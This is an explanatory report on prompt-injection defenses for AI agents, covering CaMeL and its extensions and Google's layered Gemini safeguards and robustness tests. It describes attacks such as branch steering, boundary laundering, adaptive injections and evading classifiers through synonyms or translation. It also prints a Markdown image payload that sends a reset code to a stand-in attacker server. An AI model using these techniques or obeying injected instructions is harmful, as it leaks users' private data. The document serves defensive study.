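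Bhagwatkar and colleagues compared CaMeL's running time with that of their own filter, a language model that rewrites each tool's output to remove suspicious text. On the banking and Slack tasks without attacks, CaMeL took 839 seconds in total and the filter took 700. With attacks present, CaMeL took 8,417 seconds and the filter took 3,348. The filter also completed more of the tasks in the AgentDojo benchmark and stopped all of the benchmark's standard attacks. But when the researchers tried harder attacks on the Slack tasks, 30 percent got past the filter. Fixed templates that disguised the instruction as harmless information accounted for 12.5 percentage points, and attacks that another model revised in response to the filter added 17.5. The researchers did not try these attacks against CaMeL. Rewording alone would not change CaMeL's tags, so an attacker would need a different approach.

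### Agents that click on a screen

AgentDojo's agents call tools with clear names and inputs, such as `send_email`. Computer-use agents instead operate ordinary software by looking at screenshots, clicking, and typing. They normally look at the screen before every action, which CaMeL's planner is not allowed to do.

Foerster and colleagues adapted CaMeL to this setting in January 2026. The planner writes one long program meant to cover everything that might appear on the screen. At each step, a quarantined model that can read images describes the screen, and a second query compares the description with the possibilities written into the program, such as a cookie notice showing. The interpreter then follows the matching branch. Ilia Shumailov, a CaMeL author now at the AI Sequrity Company, co-wrote this study and the one by Peters-Gill and colleagues, so neither is wholly independent.

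These programs were much longer than those for AgentDojo, averaging 41.1 tool calls and 39.7 branches compared with 4.9 and 3.7. About half of each program was fallback steps that a given run did not use. The adapted system relied on the detailed instructions to the planner and the comparison step. It succeeded on 35 of 60 tasks within three attempts, while a version without them succeeded on 11.

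The main result is that the design kept up to 57 percent of a frontier model's performance on OSWorld, a benchmark of tasks in programs such as Chrome and LibreOffice. Claude Sonnet 4.5, working without CaMeL and limited to 15 steps, had solved 109 tasks. Foerster and colleagues gave the CaMeL version five attempts at each of those tasks, and it solved 62 (57 percent) at least once. This measure, called *pass@5*, reflects performance in actual use only if something can pick out the successful attempt. On the first attempt alone, the CaMeL version solved 31 tasks, or 28.4 percent.

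The single-attempt figure is closer to what a user would experience, since an agent cannot send an email five times and keep the best version. It may slightly understate CaMeL's relative performance, because the comparison includes only tasks that the undefended agent had solved, and that agent might not solve them all again. The reported gain of up to 19 percent for a small open model, UI-TARS, also depends on extra attempts. The CaMeL version beat the undefended model's single attempt when given three attempts, but with one attempt each, it solved 51 of 339 tasks and the undefended model solved 60.

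The system used 1.88 times as many tokens as the undefended agent. A version based on FIDES, which calls the planner again at every step, used 29.6 times as many. Planning everything at the start makes an agent less flexible, but it uses far fewer tokens than planning in isolation one step at a time.

### Branch steering

A program with 40 branches gives an attacker many possible paths. In *branch steering*, the attacker misleads the quarantined model about what is on the screen, so that the program takes a branch the attacker prefers while the agent stays within its plan. For example, nearly every plan for browsing the web has a branch for dismissing cookie notices. An attacker can buy an advertisement and make it look like a cookie notice, and the agent may click it and land on the attacker's site.

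The choice between sending Bob's email and saving it as a draft was a mild case of the same problem. It is worse for a computer-use agent because the agent's actions give a policy little information to check. A policy can check the recipient of `send_email`, but a click at a given screen position might close a notice, delete a file or open a malicious page. Foerster and colleagues therefore ran their system without policies.

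They tried two other checks. One compared the quarantined model's answer with the page's underlying code, and the other asked a second model whether the answer matched the screenshot. They found attacks that got past each check, and making the checks stricter made them flag harmless pages too. Both checks rely on a model's judgment, so this part of CaMeL's protection is probabilistic, like that of the defenses it was meant to improve on.

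The tests assumed an attacker who knew the user's task and could roughly predict the plan. That is plausible for common routines such as dismissing cookie notices. It is much less plausible for a bank transfer, where the attacker would have to mislead the quarantined model several times in a row and in the right order. Even then, the attacker could not trigger any action outside the planner's original plan.

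### Several agents working together

Developers increasingly divide work among several agents, with one coordinating the others. Peters-Gill and colleagues found in October 2026 that such a system is not secure even if every agent uses CaMeL, because each agent treats a message from another agent as a trusted request from its user.

In their example, a user asks for a summary of job applicants to be sent to Julie on Slack. The coordinating agent's program looks roughly like this:

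```
info    = database_agent("Get all job applicant information.")
summary = ask_quarantined("Summarize this.", info)
notification_agent(f"Send this summary to Julie on Slack: {summary}")
```

An attacker has planted an instruction in the database to email the data to an outside address. The first two agents handle it safely because it never reaches their planners. But the last line pastes the summary, which includes the attacker's instruction, into the request to the notification agent. That agent's planner treats the whole request as coming from its user and writes a program that also sends the email. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this *boundary laundering* because text that was untrusted in one agent becomes trusted in the next.

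They also prove that the problem is general. Suppose a system has at least two agents and a tool that returns untrusted data, and users can ask an agent to pass one tool's result to another tool or agent. Then at least one possible request lets untrusted data shape an agent's plan, so the system as a whole lacks control-flow integrity. The proof does not imply that every request is at risk.

Their solution, multi-CaMeL, gives agents a shared protocol with separate channels for instructions and data:

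```
notification_agent("Send the summary to Julie on Slack.",
                   variables={"summary": summary})
```

The receiving planner sees only the sentence. The interpreter rejects any call where that sentence depends on a tool's output. Each value keeps its tags when it passes to the next agent.

Peters-Gill and colleagues tested the protocol on a version of AgentDojo that divides each group of tools among several agents. They ran 949 attacks on each of five models in each setup, with no security policies.

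| Attack success rate | No CaMeL | Separate CaMeL agents | Shared protocol |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Average | 12.9% | 0.2% | 0.0% |

Separate CaMeL agents stopped nearly every attack, and the attacks that succeeded were all boundary laundering. The success rate was probably low because these tasks seldom pass injected text from one agent to another, and attacks written to exploit this gap might succeed more often. The shared protocol closes the gap but does not prevent branch steering, and without policies it does not stop an attacker from changing an address.

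### Leaks through the interpreter

CaMeL's policies can also fail when a tag is wrong. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL tags the result as trusted when an untrusted value is inserted into fixed text. Planners routinely build text this way, as the coordinating agent does in its last line, so this fault could matter in ordinary use.

CaMeL can also leak information through branches that the program does not take. Suppose a program sets a variable `rich` to true and changes it to false only if the user's bank balance is low. If the balance is high, the variable never changes, so the interpreter does not mark it as secret. A policy that protects secrets would then let the program act on `rich`, even though its value reveals something about the balance. An outside attacker cannot add such code and would have to rely on the planner to write it.

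The retry loop creates a slower leak. Whether a policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt may reveal one yes-or-no fact about the secret, and repeated attempts can reveal all of it. Peters-Gill and colleagues avoided this by leaving retries out of their version, which still has the branch fault.

Other leaks would remain even if every tag were correct. Tallam and Miller describe a program that requests a web page N times, where N is a secret number. Whoever runs the website can count the requests and learn the number, although no request contains it. Errors and running times can also leak information. Tallam and Miller suggest limiting such loops and combining repeated requests into one, but they report no experiments measuring how often real plans leak this way.

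### Do stronger models shrink the cost?

CaMeL reduces utility less when the models are stronger. On AssetOpsBench, giving each agent its own CaMeL lowered utility by an average of 21.6 points across five models, but by only 13.4 points for the two strongest, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. The shared protocol lowered it by a further 3.2 points on average, and by less than one point for those two. The difference was similar in *AutoDojo*, where GPT-4o-mini lost 40 points and the newer GPT-5.4-mini lost 25. Foerster and colleagues found that the choice of planner mattered far more than the choice of model reading the screen.

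The trend is less clear among small models. Within the Gemma 4 family, the share of episodes without a runnable program fell from 22.9 percent on the smallest model to 3.3 percent on the largest. But across all 15 models they tested, Xu and colleagues found no significant relationship between a model's general ability and how often its programs failed. Writing CaMeL programs seems to be a specific skill that some capable small models lack.

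Better planners can write working code and account for more possible outcomes, but they can't complete a task when a policy forbids a step it requires. That may be why GPT-5.2 and MiMo-v2.5 dropped to the same score when Garby and colleagues turned the policies on. Better planners also can't include steps that appear only in a file they aren't allowed to read. Reducing these failures would take different policies, more questions to the user, or weaker isolation.

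GPT-5.5 resisted every attack in the multi-agent tests without CaMeL, so adding CaMeL only reduced the model's utility on that benchmark. Peters-Gill and colleagues caution that this doesn't show GPT-5.5 is immune, because the tests used a fixed set of attacks, and participants in a large public competition found some adaptive attacks that worked on every frontier model tested.

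## Which defenses does Google say it ships in Gemini?

Google's June 2025 post on layered defenses lists a specially trained model and five further layers, which cover both the Gemini app and Gemini in Workspace. Google checks what goes into the model and what comes out. CaMeL's planner never receives untrusted text, but the post describes no such separation for Gemini, which takes in the user's request together with the emails and files it needs to answer.

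### Before Gemini answers

Suppose a user asks Gemini to summarize the day's email, and one message contains a hidden instruction. Gmail's ordinary filters act first, and Google says they block more than 99.9 percent of spam, phishing and malware. That figure does not measure prompt injection, and a message with one hidden sentence may not resemble spam.

Messages that get through then go to the *content classifiers*, machine-learning models that scan emails and files for malicious instructions. Google built them from a catalog of attacks that it compiled with outside researchers, whom it pays for reporting flaws. Google was still rolling out the classifiers when it published the post.

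On its help page for Workspace administrators, Google says that if one email looks malicious, Gemini leaves it out of the summary and displays "Some content was excluded for security reasons". If every email or file behind the request looks suspicious, Gemini gives no answer and displays "A security risk was identified and blocked". On its page for Workspace users, Google adds that Gemini may refuse to answer even if only one of the emails is malicious. An attacker who fails to steal anything can still prevent the user from getting a summary.

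The classifiers are probabilistic, so they can miss attacks and flag harmless messages. Nicolas Lidzborski, a security engineer at Google Workspace, said in a March 2026 talk that attackers can get past them by swapping in synonyms or translating the instruction into a less common language, according to *Securing Workspace GenAI at Google* (2026), notes made from the transcript and slides. Filters that read only text also miss instructions hidden in images or audio. Lidzborski recommended removing hidden text before the model reads a message, so that the model receives only what the user would see. That step is deterministic, but it doesn't remove instructions that are visible to the user.

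Google calls the next layer *security thought reinforcement*. It surrounds the content with instructions reminding the model to do what the user asked and ignore any commands in the material. The reminder doesn't scan the content and works only if the model follows it. A diagram in the June 2025 post shows that Gemini may block a response at this stage even after the classifiers have passed the content. Lidzborski said that this kind of measure, which also includes special markers around untrusted content, was "absolutely not perfect" but made attacks a little harder.

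The remaining protection at this stage comes from the model's training. Google trained Gemini 2.5 on attack examples so that it would more often ignore injected commands and continue with the user's task. Google DeepMind's *Advancing Gemini's security safeguards* (2025) called Gemini 2.5 the company's most secure model family to date. The training doesn't always work, and because it targets commands, a false statement in an email can still end up in the summary.

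### Images and links in the answer

A model's answer can leak data even if the agent never calls a tool. Chat applications commonly let the model write in Markdown, a simple notation for formatting text, and convert the result into a web page. An injected instruction can tell the model to include an image whose address contains private data:

```
![logo](ATTACKER-SERVER/logo.png?note=reset-code-481516)
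```

To display the image, the user's device requests that address from the attacker's server. The address contains the reset code, so the code appears in the server's log as soon as the request arrives, even if the image doesn't exist. The user hasn't clicked anything and sees at most a broken image icon.

Google's *markdown sanitizer* identifies external image URLs in Gemini's answers and doesn't render them. This prevents image requests from carrying data to an attacker's server, whatever the model has written. Google says that Gemini is therefore not exposed to EchoLeak, a vulnerability that leaked data through images without a click. The rule is deterministic and doesn't depend on judging whether a particular image is malicious, so it also blocks harmless external images. It doesn't stop data from leaking through other routes, such as an email the agent sends or a link the user clicks.

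Gemini checks links using Safe Browsing, Google's service for identifying dangerous websites. If a document contains a link that the service flags as unsafe, Gemini's summary shows "suspicious link removed" in its place. Gavish classes this as a deterministic defense, and the removal does follow a fixed rule. But flagging a link depends on the information Safe Browsing has about the site, so a link to a newly created site may get through.

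Lidzborski described another rule, *link grounding*, which removes URLs the model produces that have no source in the material it read. An attacker doesn't know the user's private data in advance, so they can't write a URL containing it into an email, and the model has to assemble the URL itself. Link grounding could therefore catch a leak even when the URL points to a site with a clean reputation.

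### Confirmations and notices

Gemini asks the user to confirm certain risky actions before it carries them out. In Google's example, a user tells Gemini to delete everything on Saturday's calendar, and Gemini lists the three events it found and waits for approval. This layer checks the proposed action, so rewording the instruction that led to it doesn't help an attacker.

Gavish also counts confirmation among the deterministic defenses. A fixed rule can trigger the request, but the user decides whether the action goes ahead. Lidzborski shared Tallam and Miller's concern about frequent requests, warning that users become "approval bots". Some actions don't require confirmation, and a misleading summary never triggers a request because Gemini only displays it.

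In the last of the five layers, Gemini notifies the user after another defense has acted. The notice links to a help article so that the user can watch for similar attacks. It can't appear for an attack that the other layers missed, so a user who sees no notice can't conclude that the content was safe.

### Analysis: Bob's document in Gemini

Google has not published a trace showing how these layers handle an attack, so the table is inferred from its descriptions of them. It covers the two attacks on Bob's document: the added sentence about forwarding the user's inbox and the changed address. The table assumes that Gemini asks the user before sending email, as Google says its later agent, Gemini Spark, does.

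| Layer | Added sentence | Changed address |
|---|---|---|
| Content classifiers | May flag the notes and exclude them | Find no instruction to flag |
| Reminders and model training | May lead Gemini to ignore the sentence | Don't apply, since the user asked Gemini to use the address |
| Image and link checks | Don't apply, since the data leaves by email | Don't apply |
| User confirmation | Shows a forwarding request the user didn't make | Shows the expected email with the wrong address |
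| Notice to the user | Appears if a classifier flags the notes | Doesn't appear |

Several layers could stop the added sentence, but their failures are not independent. Wording that a classifier labels harmless may also make Gemini follow the instruction, because both are models that process the same text. The confirmation request is the best safeguard here if the other layers fail, because a user who asked to send one document will probably notice a request to forward the inbox.

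A correct detection can also prevent Gemini from completing the user's task. The notes contain Bob's address and the document's name, so if Gemini excludes the notes, it can't send him the document. CaMeL can often still finish the task because it doesn't have to exclude them.

Only the user can stop the second attack, by noticing the wrong address in the confirmation request. Users who have to confirm every email expect that request, so it doesn't alert them. CaMeL's example policy requires confirmation only for unfamiliar addresses, so if Bob is a contact, getting a request at all suggests that something is wrong.

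### What Google changed by April 2026

In the Workspace update, Gavish describes how Google revises its defenses as it discovers new attacks. A central policy engine now controls the deterministic defenses. Its configuration covers which tools Gemini may call, how Gemini handles links, and which tools it may use one after another, which Gavish calls *tool chaining*. Editing a configuration is faster than retraining a model, so Google can use the engine for quick "point fixes", such as a filter that blocks text matching a known pattern.

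A pattern-matching filter is deterministic, but unlike CaMeL's tags it depends on the attacker's wording, so a reworded attack may not match. It is useful mainly as a stopgap while Google updates its other defenses.

Those updates start from a catalog of attacks, which Google collects from its own testers, automated attack programs, outside researchers and public reports. A tool called Simula generates variations on each attack. Google retrains its classifiers on some of the variations and tests them on others it held back. It uses the same material to revise the written instructions in its prompts, keeping changes that improve the results. Finally, it simulates attacks on applications such as Gmail and Docs with and without each change.

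This process should help most against attacks that resemble known ones. It offers no guarantee against a new kind of attack. The changed address in Bob's notes would be hard to turn into training data, because a classifier that learned to flag unfamiliar email addresses would also flag a lot of ordinary mail.

### Tool-chaining policies

Gavish mentions tool chaining without explaining it. The notes on Lidzborski's talk describe one rule that stops the agent from fetching anything external after it has accessed Workspace data. [un]prompted's *Securing Workspace GenAI at Google Speed* (2026), the conference abstract for the talk, lists "chaining policies for sandboxing rogue agent actions" among the strategies for protecting Gemini and Workspace.

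The software that runs the tools has to keep a record of the session to apply such a rule. According to the notes, it tracks how risky the session has become and withdraws some abilities as new data comes in. An early version of Gemini had a simpler limit. Embrace The Red's *Google Gemini* found that this limit blocked automatic access to Workspace data after untrusted content arrived, but only until the user's next message.

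CaMeL's checks apply to the values in a particular call. This simplified code shows the difference:

```
# Tool chaining: what has this session already done?
if session.has_read_workspace_data and tool == "fetch_external_page":
    block()

# Value tracking: what is in this call?
if tool == "fetch_external_page" and is_private(page_address):
    block()
```

If a user asks Gemini to summarize a contract in Drive and then to get tomorrow's weather from a public website, the chaining rule blocks the weather request. The rule applies because Gemini has already read Workspace data in that session, even though the request contains none of that data. CaMeL could allow the request because the weather page's address doesn't depend on the contract.

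However, the cruder rule is harder to get around. It blocks every request after the agent has read the secret, so it stops even the leak through repeated page requests that Tallam and Miller describe. It also doesn't need individual values to be tagged accurately.

In the example of Bob's document, rules on tool chaining can't distinguish the user's request from the attack. The request requires the agent to read the notes and then send an email, and the attack uses the same two tools in the same order but changes the address. A rule about that sequence would therefore block both or allow both. Google could require confirmation whenever an email follows untrusted content, but the user would then have to decide whether to send it.

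The agent can also still choose among the permitted sequences after reading the attacker's text, whereas CaMeL fixes the possible sequences beforehand. Lidzborski did recommend tracking the origin and sensitivity of data throughout an agent's work, which sounds closer to CaMeL. It's unclear from the notes whether Google tracks individual values through what the model writes or only labels the documents that enter a session, and Gavish doesn't describe any value tracking.

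Lidzborski proposed a more flexible check for irreversible actions. The agent states what it intends to do, and a gatekeeper compares that with the user's intent and a policy generated for the situation before the action runs. He named a framework for this, probably Conseca, though the transcript garbles the name. Conseca is a design for contextual agent security by Lillian Tsai and Eugene Bagdasarian. UMass Amherst's *Bagdasarian's Contextual Agent Security Adopted in Google Cloud Gemini Enterprise* reports that Google now uses their design in its Gemini Enterprise Agent Platform, a service for building agents, to compare proposed tool calls with the user's intent and plain-language rules.

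Such a check could distinguish requests that a fixed sequence rule treats alike. It probably also relies on a model's judgment again, because software has to interpret a plain-language rule to apply it. The university's announcement is about the platform and doesn't show that the Gemini app or Spark has the same protection.

### Narrower permissions in Workspace Studio

Google documented another combination of defenses in August 2026 for Workspace Studio, where users build automated flows without writing code. *Defend against agentic risks with multi-layered protections in Google Workspace Studio* (Quinney, 2026) describes classifiers that examine the prompt, the surrounding content and the output for signs that a flow has drifted from its purpose. If they detect an injection, Studio halts the flow.

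Studio also gives each flow its own identity, with only the permissions its task needs. A flow that sends email through Gmail can't open files in Drive, even though its owner can. This restriction is deterministic and still holds after an injection succeeds. The attacker can still misuse anything the flow can access, which in Quinney's example includes the owner's Gmail data.

Administrators can require the flow's owner to approve any email to someone outside the organization. This could help with the changed address, because if Bob is a colleague and the attacker is an outsider, only the tampered email needs approval. Studio only has to check the recipient, not where the address came from. If Bob is also an outsider, both emails need approval, so the rule doesn't distinguish them. It also misses an attacker inside the organization.

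Other rules concern the data itself. An administrator can keep Gemini from using Drive files with a certain label, such as "Financial". Studio can also allow an action, block it or ask for confirmation, depending on which data a flow has used and who will be able to see the result. These rules resemble CaMeL's policies about who may read a value, although Quinney doesn't describe tags that follow individual values through a flow. As with CaMeL, someone has to write the rules and label the files correctly.

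### Gemini Spark and the isolated machine

Google announced Gemini Spark in May 2026 as a personal agent that can work in the background at any hour. It can read and send email, edit documents, browse the web and run code. Google said at the time that users would choose whether to turn Spark on and that it would ask them before taking high-stakes actions, such as sending email or adding calendar events.

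The day after the announcement, Willison (2026) looked for an explanation of how Spark would handle prompt injection. The best he found was a passage for business customers in *Everything Google Cloud customers need to know coming out of Google I/O* (Kurian, 2026). According to the passage, each task runs in a new, isolated virtual machine, a simulated computer that exists only for that task. The passage also says that the agent never sees the user's login credentials and that its traffic passes through a gateway that enforces rules against data loss.

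Isolating the machine keeps one session's data out of another and should limit the damage if the agent runs malicious code. But an injected instruction can still make Spark forward an email from inside the isolated machine, because the user has given it access to Gmail. Hiding passwords from the agent prevents an attacker from stealing them through it, but the attacker may still be able to make the agent act on the account.

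The gateway is more directly relevant to injection because a data-loss rule can stop a confidential file from leaving the company, whatever caused the agent to send it. It would not stop Bob's document from going to the wrong address unless a rule covered that document or recipient. Kurian also says that Spark needs explicit approval for high-risk actions such as sending email, so this defense again depends on the user's attention.

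The consumer version appears to have weaker separation between tasks. Google says in its help page *Use Gemini Spark to manage your tasks & workflows in Gemini Apps* that Spark saves data from its remote browser and remote computer for later sessions. Google also warns there that an injected instruction could install malicious software that keeps sending data out, and advises users to delete the saved data as a protection. A fresh machine for every task would remove such software without relying on users to remember to delete the data.

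### What Google tells Spark's users

The help page describes injection protections in more detail than the launch announcements. Spark asks for confirmation before it sends messages, makes purchases, submits web forms or changes the user's data. For some steps, such as entering a password or payment details, it may hand control of the browser to the user. It also shows its plan and progress, so a user who is watching can stop it.

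Google also says that Spark protects against prompt injection partly by limiting its browsing to websites and actions relevant to the task. If the limit holds, a web page about apartments couldn't send the agent to an unrelated banking site. The strength of this protection depends on how Spark determines what is relevant, which Google doesn't explain on its page. A list fixed before browsing would resemble part of CaMeL's plan, but if a model decided after reading each web page, an attacker's text could influence the decision.

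Spark can change or delete many private items in Google Tasks at once without asking the user to confirm. It does need approval to edit shared documents, but a user who approves a long edit may not notice one altered number.

Spark has also gained more sources of untrusted text and more ways to act since its launch. According to Google's *What's new for Gemini Spark* (2026), it began reading comments in Google Docs in June, and users could connect outside applications of their choice. In July, it became able to edit shared documents. A person who can comment on a document can therefore supply text to an agent that may also have access to the owner's email.

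At the end of July, Google connected Spark to Chrome, where it can use the websites a user is signed in to. Coimbra and Dsilva (2026) say in *Gemini Spark now integrates with Chrome* that Spark protects against prompt injection and hands control back to the user for payments, but they don't explain how the protection works. Chrome's browsing agent has separate defenses, including the User Alignment Critic, a model that Google Cloud describes as isolated and partly inspired by CaMeL.

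Google says that none of Spark's safeguards guarantees protection and calls the user's active supervision the most important one. Active supervision is hard to reconcile with an agent that can run 15 tasks at a time and start work on a schedule. If a scheduled task runs while the user is offline, they may be unable to stop an unintended action, so Google recommends against scheduling tasks that involve sensitive information or actions.

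## How well did Gemini's defenses hold in Google's own tests?

Google has published detailed attack success rates for one part of its defenses, the trained model. They come from the May 2025 robustness report, in which Shi and colleagues used automated tools to attack Gemini 2.0 and Gemini 2.5. Google had trained Gemini 2.5 to resist these attacks, and they succeeded less often against it on average, but the strongest still worked almost every time on one task. Both models are now out of date. Kavukcuoglu's *Gemini 4 Carbon* (2026), Google's October 2026 announcement of that model, calls it the company's strongest.

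### A made-up user with a secret

The tests use invented users and invented private data. Google's *How we estimate the risk from prompt injection attacks on AI systems*, an earlier post about the same kind of testing, describes the email version. Testers give an agent that can read and send email a fictional conversation in which the user has mentioned something private, such as a passport number. The user then asks for a summary of the latest email, which the attacker wrote. The attack succeeds if the agent sends the passport number to the attacker. Shi and colleagues ran simulated tasks with both email and a calendar.

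The attacker doesn't know the secret or what else the user has discussed. An injection therefore has to work on conversations that its author has never seen, much as a phishing email has to work on strangers. To measure this, the testers develop an injection and then try it on held-out conversations, which played no part in its development. For an injected text `t` and a model `M`, the attack success rate is

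`ASR(t, M) = held-out conversations in which M sends the secret / all held-out conversations`

At a success rate of 90 percent, the same text extracts the secret from nine in ten new conversations. An attacker could send it once to each of many people and expect it to work on most of them, unless another defense stopped it. In the earlier example, by contrast, the attacker had to keep trying because the filter missed only one attack in a hundred.

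Google uses software to write the injections because finding weaknesses by hand is slow and the models change quickly. The software tries an injection, then revises it based on the model's response. In one version, a second language model writes the injections, and the model under attack returns a score showing how likely each one is to succeed. An outsider attacking a finished product would normally see only its answers and actions. Google gave its attackers such advantages because it reasoned that weak attacks reveal little about a system's vulnerability.

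Shi and colleagues tested the model without the guardrails used in Google's products. No separate classifier screened the email, and no confirmation request appeared before the agent sent the secret. The risk to a person using the Gemini app should therefore be lower than in these tests.

The tests also leave out many kinds of harm. They measure only whether private information reaches the attacker, so they wouldn't count an injection that made the agent delete the user's mail. They don't include an attack like the changed address in Bob's meeting notes.

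### Attackers who adjust to a defense

Google also tested defenses that leave the model unchanged. Some came from other researchers and some from Google. Google DeepMind's companion post lists six.

| Defense | How it works |
|---|---|
| In-context learning | Adds examples to the prompt that show the model how to respond to attacks |
| Spotlighting | Marks untrusted text to help the model distinguish it from instructions |
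| Paraphrasing | Rewords untrusted text so that the attacker's exact wording doesn't reach the model |
| Classifier | Uses a model to check text for signs of an attack |
| Self-reflection | Asks the model to check its own response |
| Perplexity filter | Flags text that a language model finds improbable, such as a string of random characters |

These defenses showed promise against basic attacks that weren't designed to get around them. The researchers then used adaptive attacks, in which software tests injections against the defended model and revises them until they succeed. For example, a perplexity filter may catch a string of random characters, but an adaptive attack can favor ordinary sentences to avoid the filter. Google DeepMind found that spotlighting and self-reflection, which had worked well against the basic attacks, were much less effective against adaptive ones.

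In 24 cases, Shi and colleagues compared adaptive attacks, which are tailored to the defense, with static attacks, which stay the same whatever the defense. The adaptive attack did at least as well in 16 cases and worse in the other eight.

That result looks odd, because an attacker who knows about a defense can still use the static attack, so should never do worse. A plausible explanation is that a defense makes the search harder, and the software stopped before finding a good injection. The attacker's success rate in each case is therefore at least the higher of the two measured rates.

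The same reasoning applies to any low attack success rate in these tests. A rate of 90 percent means the testers found an effective injection, but a rate of 5 percent shows only that they didn't find one with the time and information they had. CaMeL's guarantee about the steps in a plan doesn't depend on how hard anyone has searched for an attack.

### Training on attacks that worked

Google used adversarial training, which it also calls model hardening, to try to improve the model's own responses. It first assembled varied scenarios in which an agent uses tools and reads outside content. It then used automated attacks to find injections that made Gemini mishandle sensitive information in those scenarios. Google paired the successful injections with corrected responses, in which the model carries out the user's request and ignores the attacker's.

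If the user asked for a summary of an email, the corrected response is the summary, with no message to the attacker. A refusal would also protect the secret, but the user wouldn't get the summary. Successful attacks are the most useful training examples because they show where the model still goes wrong.

Google used this material for supervised fine-tuning, which trains a model to reproduce example responses, and for reinforcement learning, in which the model produces its own responses and training makes the highly rewarded ones more likely. A reward can apply to any response the model produces, including mistakes the examples didn't anticipate.

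The training makes Gemini less likely to obey an injected command but doesn't rule it out, and Google DeepMind acknowledges that "no model is completely immune".

Google used automated attackers both to produce the training examples and to test the trained model, so Gemini may have become especially good at resisting the kinds of text those attackers write. A human attacker, or a program that searches differently, might find weaknesses that neither the training nor the tests covered.

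### From Gemini 2.0 to Gemini 2.5

Shi and colleagues report that attack success fell by about 47 percent on average from Gemini 2.0 to Gemini 2.5. This appears to be the average fall in percentage points across their results, rather than a proportional reduction. A 47-point fall from 90 to 43 percent would eliminate about half of the successful attacks, while one from 60 to 13 percent would eliminate more than three-quarters.

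Gemini 2.5 was a new generation of the model and included changes besides adversarial training, so comparing the two generations can't show how much of the improvement came from that training.

On the calendar task, the strongest attack still succeeded against Gemini 2.5 in 94.6 percent of tests. An attacker with several methods would use the one that works best, so the highest success rate is a better measure than the average of how far Google can rely on the model alone.

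Old attacks gave a much more favorable picture. Their success rate fell from 92 percent to 18 percent. Someone who ran only that test would conclude that Gemini now resisted about four in five of the attacks that used to work, and might reasonably think the problem was nearly under control. The adaptive test differs only in which model the attacker works against:

```
# Static test: reuse an attack written for the old model
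attack = search_for_attack(old_model)
rate   = attack_success_rate(attack, new_model)

# Adaptive test: write an attack for the new model
attack = search_for_attack(new_model)
rate   = attack_success_rate(attack, new_model)
```

The static result still has some value. Many attackers presumably reuse published injections, and a model that resists most of these protects its users from those attackers. But the result doesn't show how the model would do against someone willing to write a new attack, which is the danger for a product as widely used as Gemini.

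The same distinction affects how much confidence to place in Google's later updates to Workspace. A retrained classifier could score well on held-back variations of known attacks and still fail against an attacker who kept revising a message until it got through. Google's automated red-teaming does revise its attacks like this, but Gavish describes it as a way to discover attacks and check security controls, and doesn't report how well the classifiers performed.

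*AutoDojo* showed that even fixed attacks could still work on an undefended Gemini 2.5 Flash. Its tests used different tasks, tools and attacker goals from Google's, so the two sets of rates aren't directly comparable. But the results suggest that resistance learned in one setting may not carry over to another.

### What a warning added

When Shi and colleagues added a warning to the prompt, the 94.6 percent attack success rate on the calendar task fell to 6.2 percent. This change to the prompt alone reduced the rate by far more than the average improvement from Gemini 2.0 to Gemini 2.5. Training and warnings may work better together, since a model that has learned to ignore embedded commands may respond better to a warning about them.

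Shi and colleagues doubt that the result generalizes, and the test was narrow, which supports their caution. Every attack was an attempt to get private information to an outsider, which the simulated user never wanted. A warning against doing that has no downside in the test because it doesn't conflict with any legitimate request.

Some ordinary requests conflict with the warning, such as asking Gemini to send a landlord the details requested in an email. A warning strict enough to stop every injected command could also block that request, while a more permissive one would leave Gemini to determine which of the email's requests serve the user's purpose.

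The warning's effect could also change with a different injection, a longer document or a new version of Gemini. Google's products use a similar reminder, but the 6.2 percent rate doesn't measure how well that reminder works, because Gemini does more varied tasks in those products and attackers have more goals.

### Did the training make Gemini less useful?

A model trained to ignore instructions in emails might also ignore instructions the user wants it to follow, treat harmless messages as suspicious, or leave tasks unfinished. Shi and colleagues say adversarial training did not reduce Gemini's general ability. In the companion post, Google DeepMind says more cautiously that the training lowered the attack success rate "without significantly impacting" performance on normal tasks, but gives no scores. Gavish made a similar claim about model hardening in April 2026, also without figures.

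If the claim is right, adversarial training costs users very little, whereas agents running CaMeL completed far fewer AgentDojo tasks.

Adversarial training could leave a model's mathematics and coding scores unchanged but make it worse at handling an email that contains legitimate instructions. To detect this, researchers would need to test the same model with and without adversarial training on tasks where following outside instructions is correct. *AgentDyn* has suitable tasks, including some with helpful instructions from third parties.

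### Gemini 3 and Gemini 4

Google has published long safety reports on its later models, but much of their content concerns dangers other than prompt injection. Google's *Gemini 3 Pro Frontier Safety Framework Report* (2025) lists four main areas of risk: chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear information; cybersecurity; machine-learning research; and harmful manipulation. It also takes an exploratory approach to misalignment, the risk that a model pursues goals its developers didn't intend. The framework covers severe harm that a highly capable model might make possible. An email that tricks Gemini into forwarding a private document may matter a great deal to the user, but the framework doesn't list this kind of attack as a main area of risk.

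Google claimed that Gemini 3 was more resistant to prompt injection. VentureBeat compared the disclosures of four AI companies in spring 2026 and found that Google had given no figure to support this claim. The framework report covered adversarial testing in its own areas of risk, which did not include prompt injection.

Anthropic and OpenAI published figures for their models that spring, though they measured different things. Anthropic had professional testers attack Claude Opus 4.8 in 129 simulated browser environments. With the model's extended reasoning on, 31.5 percent of attempts succeeded without Anthropic's additional safeguards and 0.5 percent with them. In coding tasks, an adaptive attacker succeeded in 7.03 percent of single attempts without the safeguards and 2.09 percent with them.

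OpenAI gave GPT-5.5 a robustness score of 0.963 against known attacks that arrive through connectors, which link a model to outside services. An earlier model did better, scoring 0.998. VentureBeat warns against comparing this score with Anthropic's rates. By Shi and colleagues' argument, it is also weaker evidence of security, because attackers can use attacks the developer doesn't know about.

Google's *Gemini 4 Argon Safety & Security Report* (2026) evaluates jailbreaks in its section on adversarial robustness, including jailbreaks involving cybersecurity and chemical and biological harm. In a jailbreak, the attacker is the user, who tries to get the model to give help it is supposed to refuse.

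A model that resists jailbreaks may still be vulnerable to indirect prompt injection. A model can often recognize a dangerous request from its subject, such as how to make a weapon. But forwarding an email or sharing a file is an ordinary action, and whether it is harmful depends on who wanted it done.

More recent models may be much harder to attack than the ones in the 2025 report. PromptArmor, a security company, says its *FrontierBreach* benchmark is the only known one on which any attack has succeeded against Gemini 4 Carbon. Although the company is describing its own product, its claim is another reason not to treat the 94.6 percent rate as an estimate for Gemini today.

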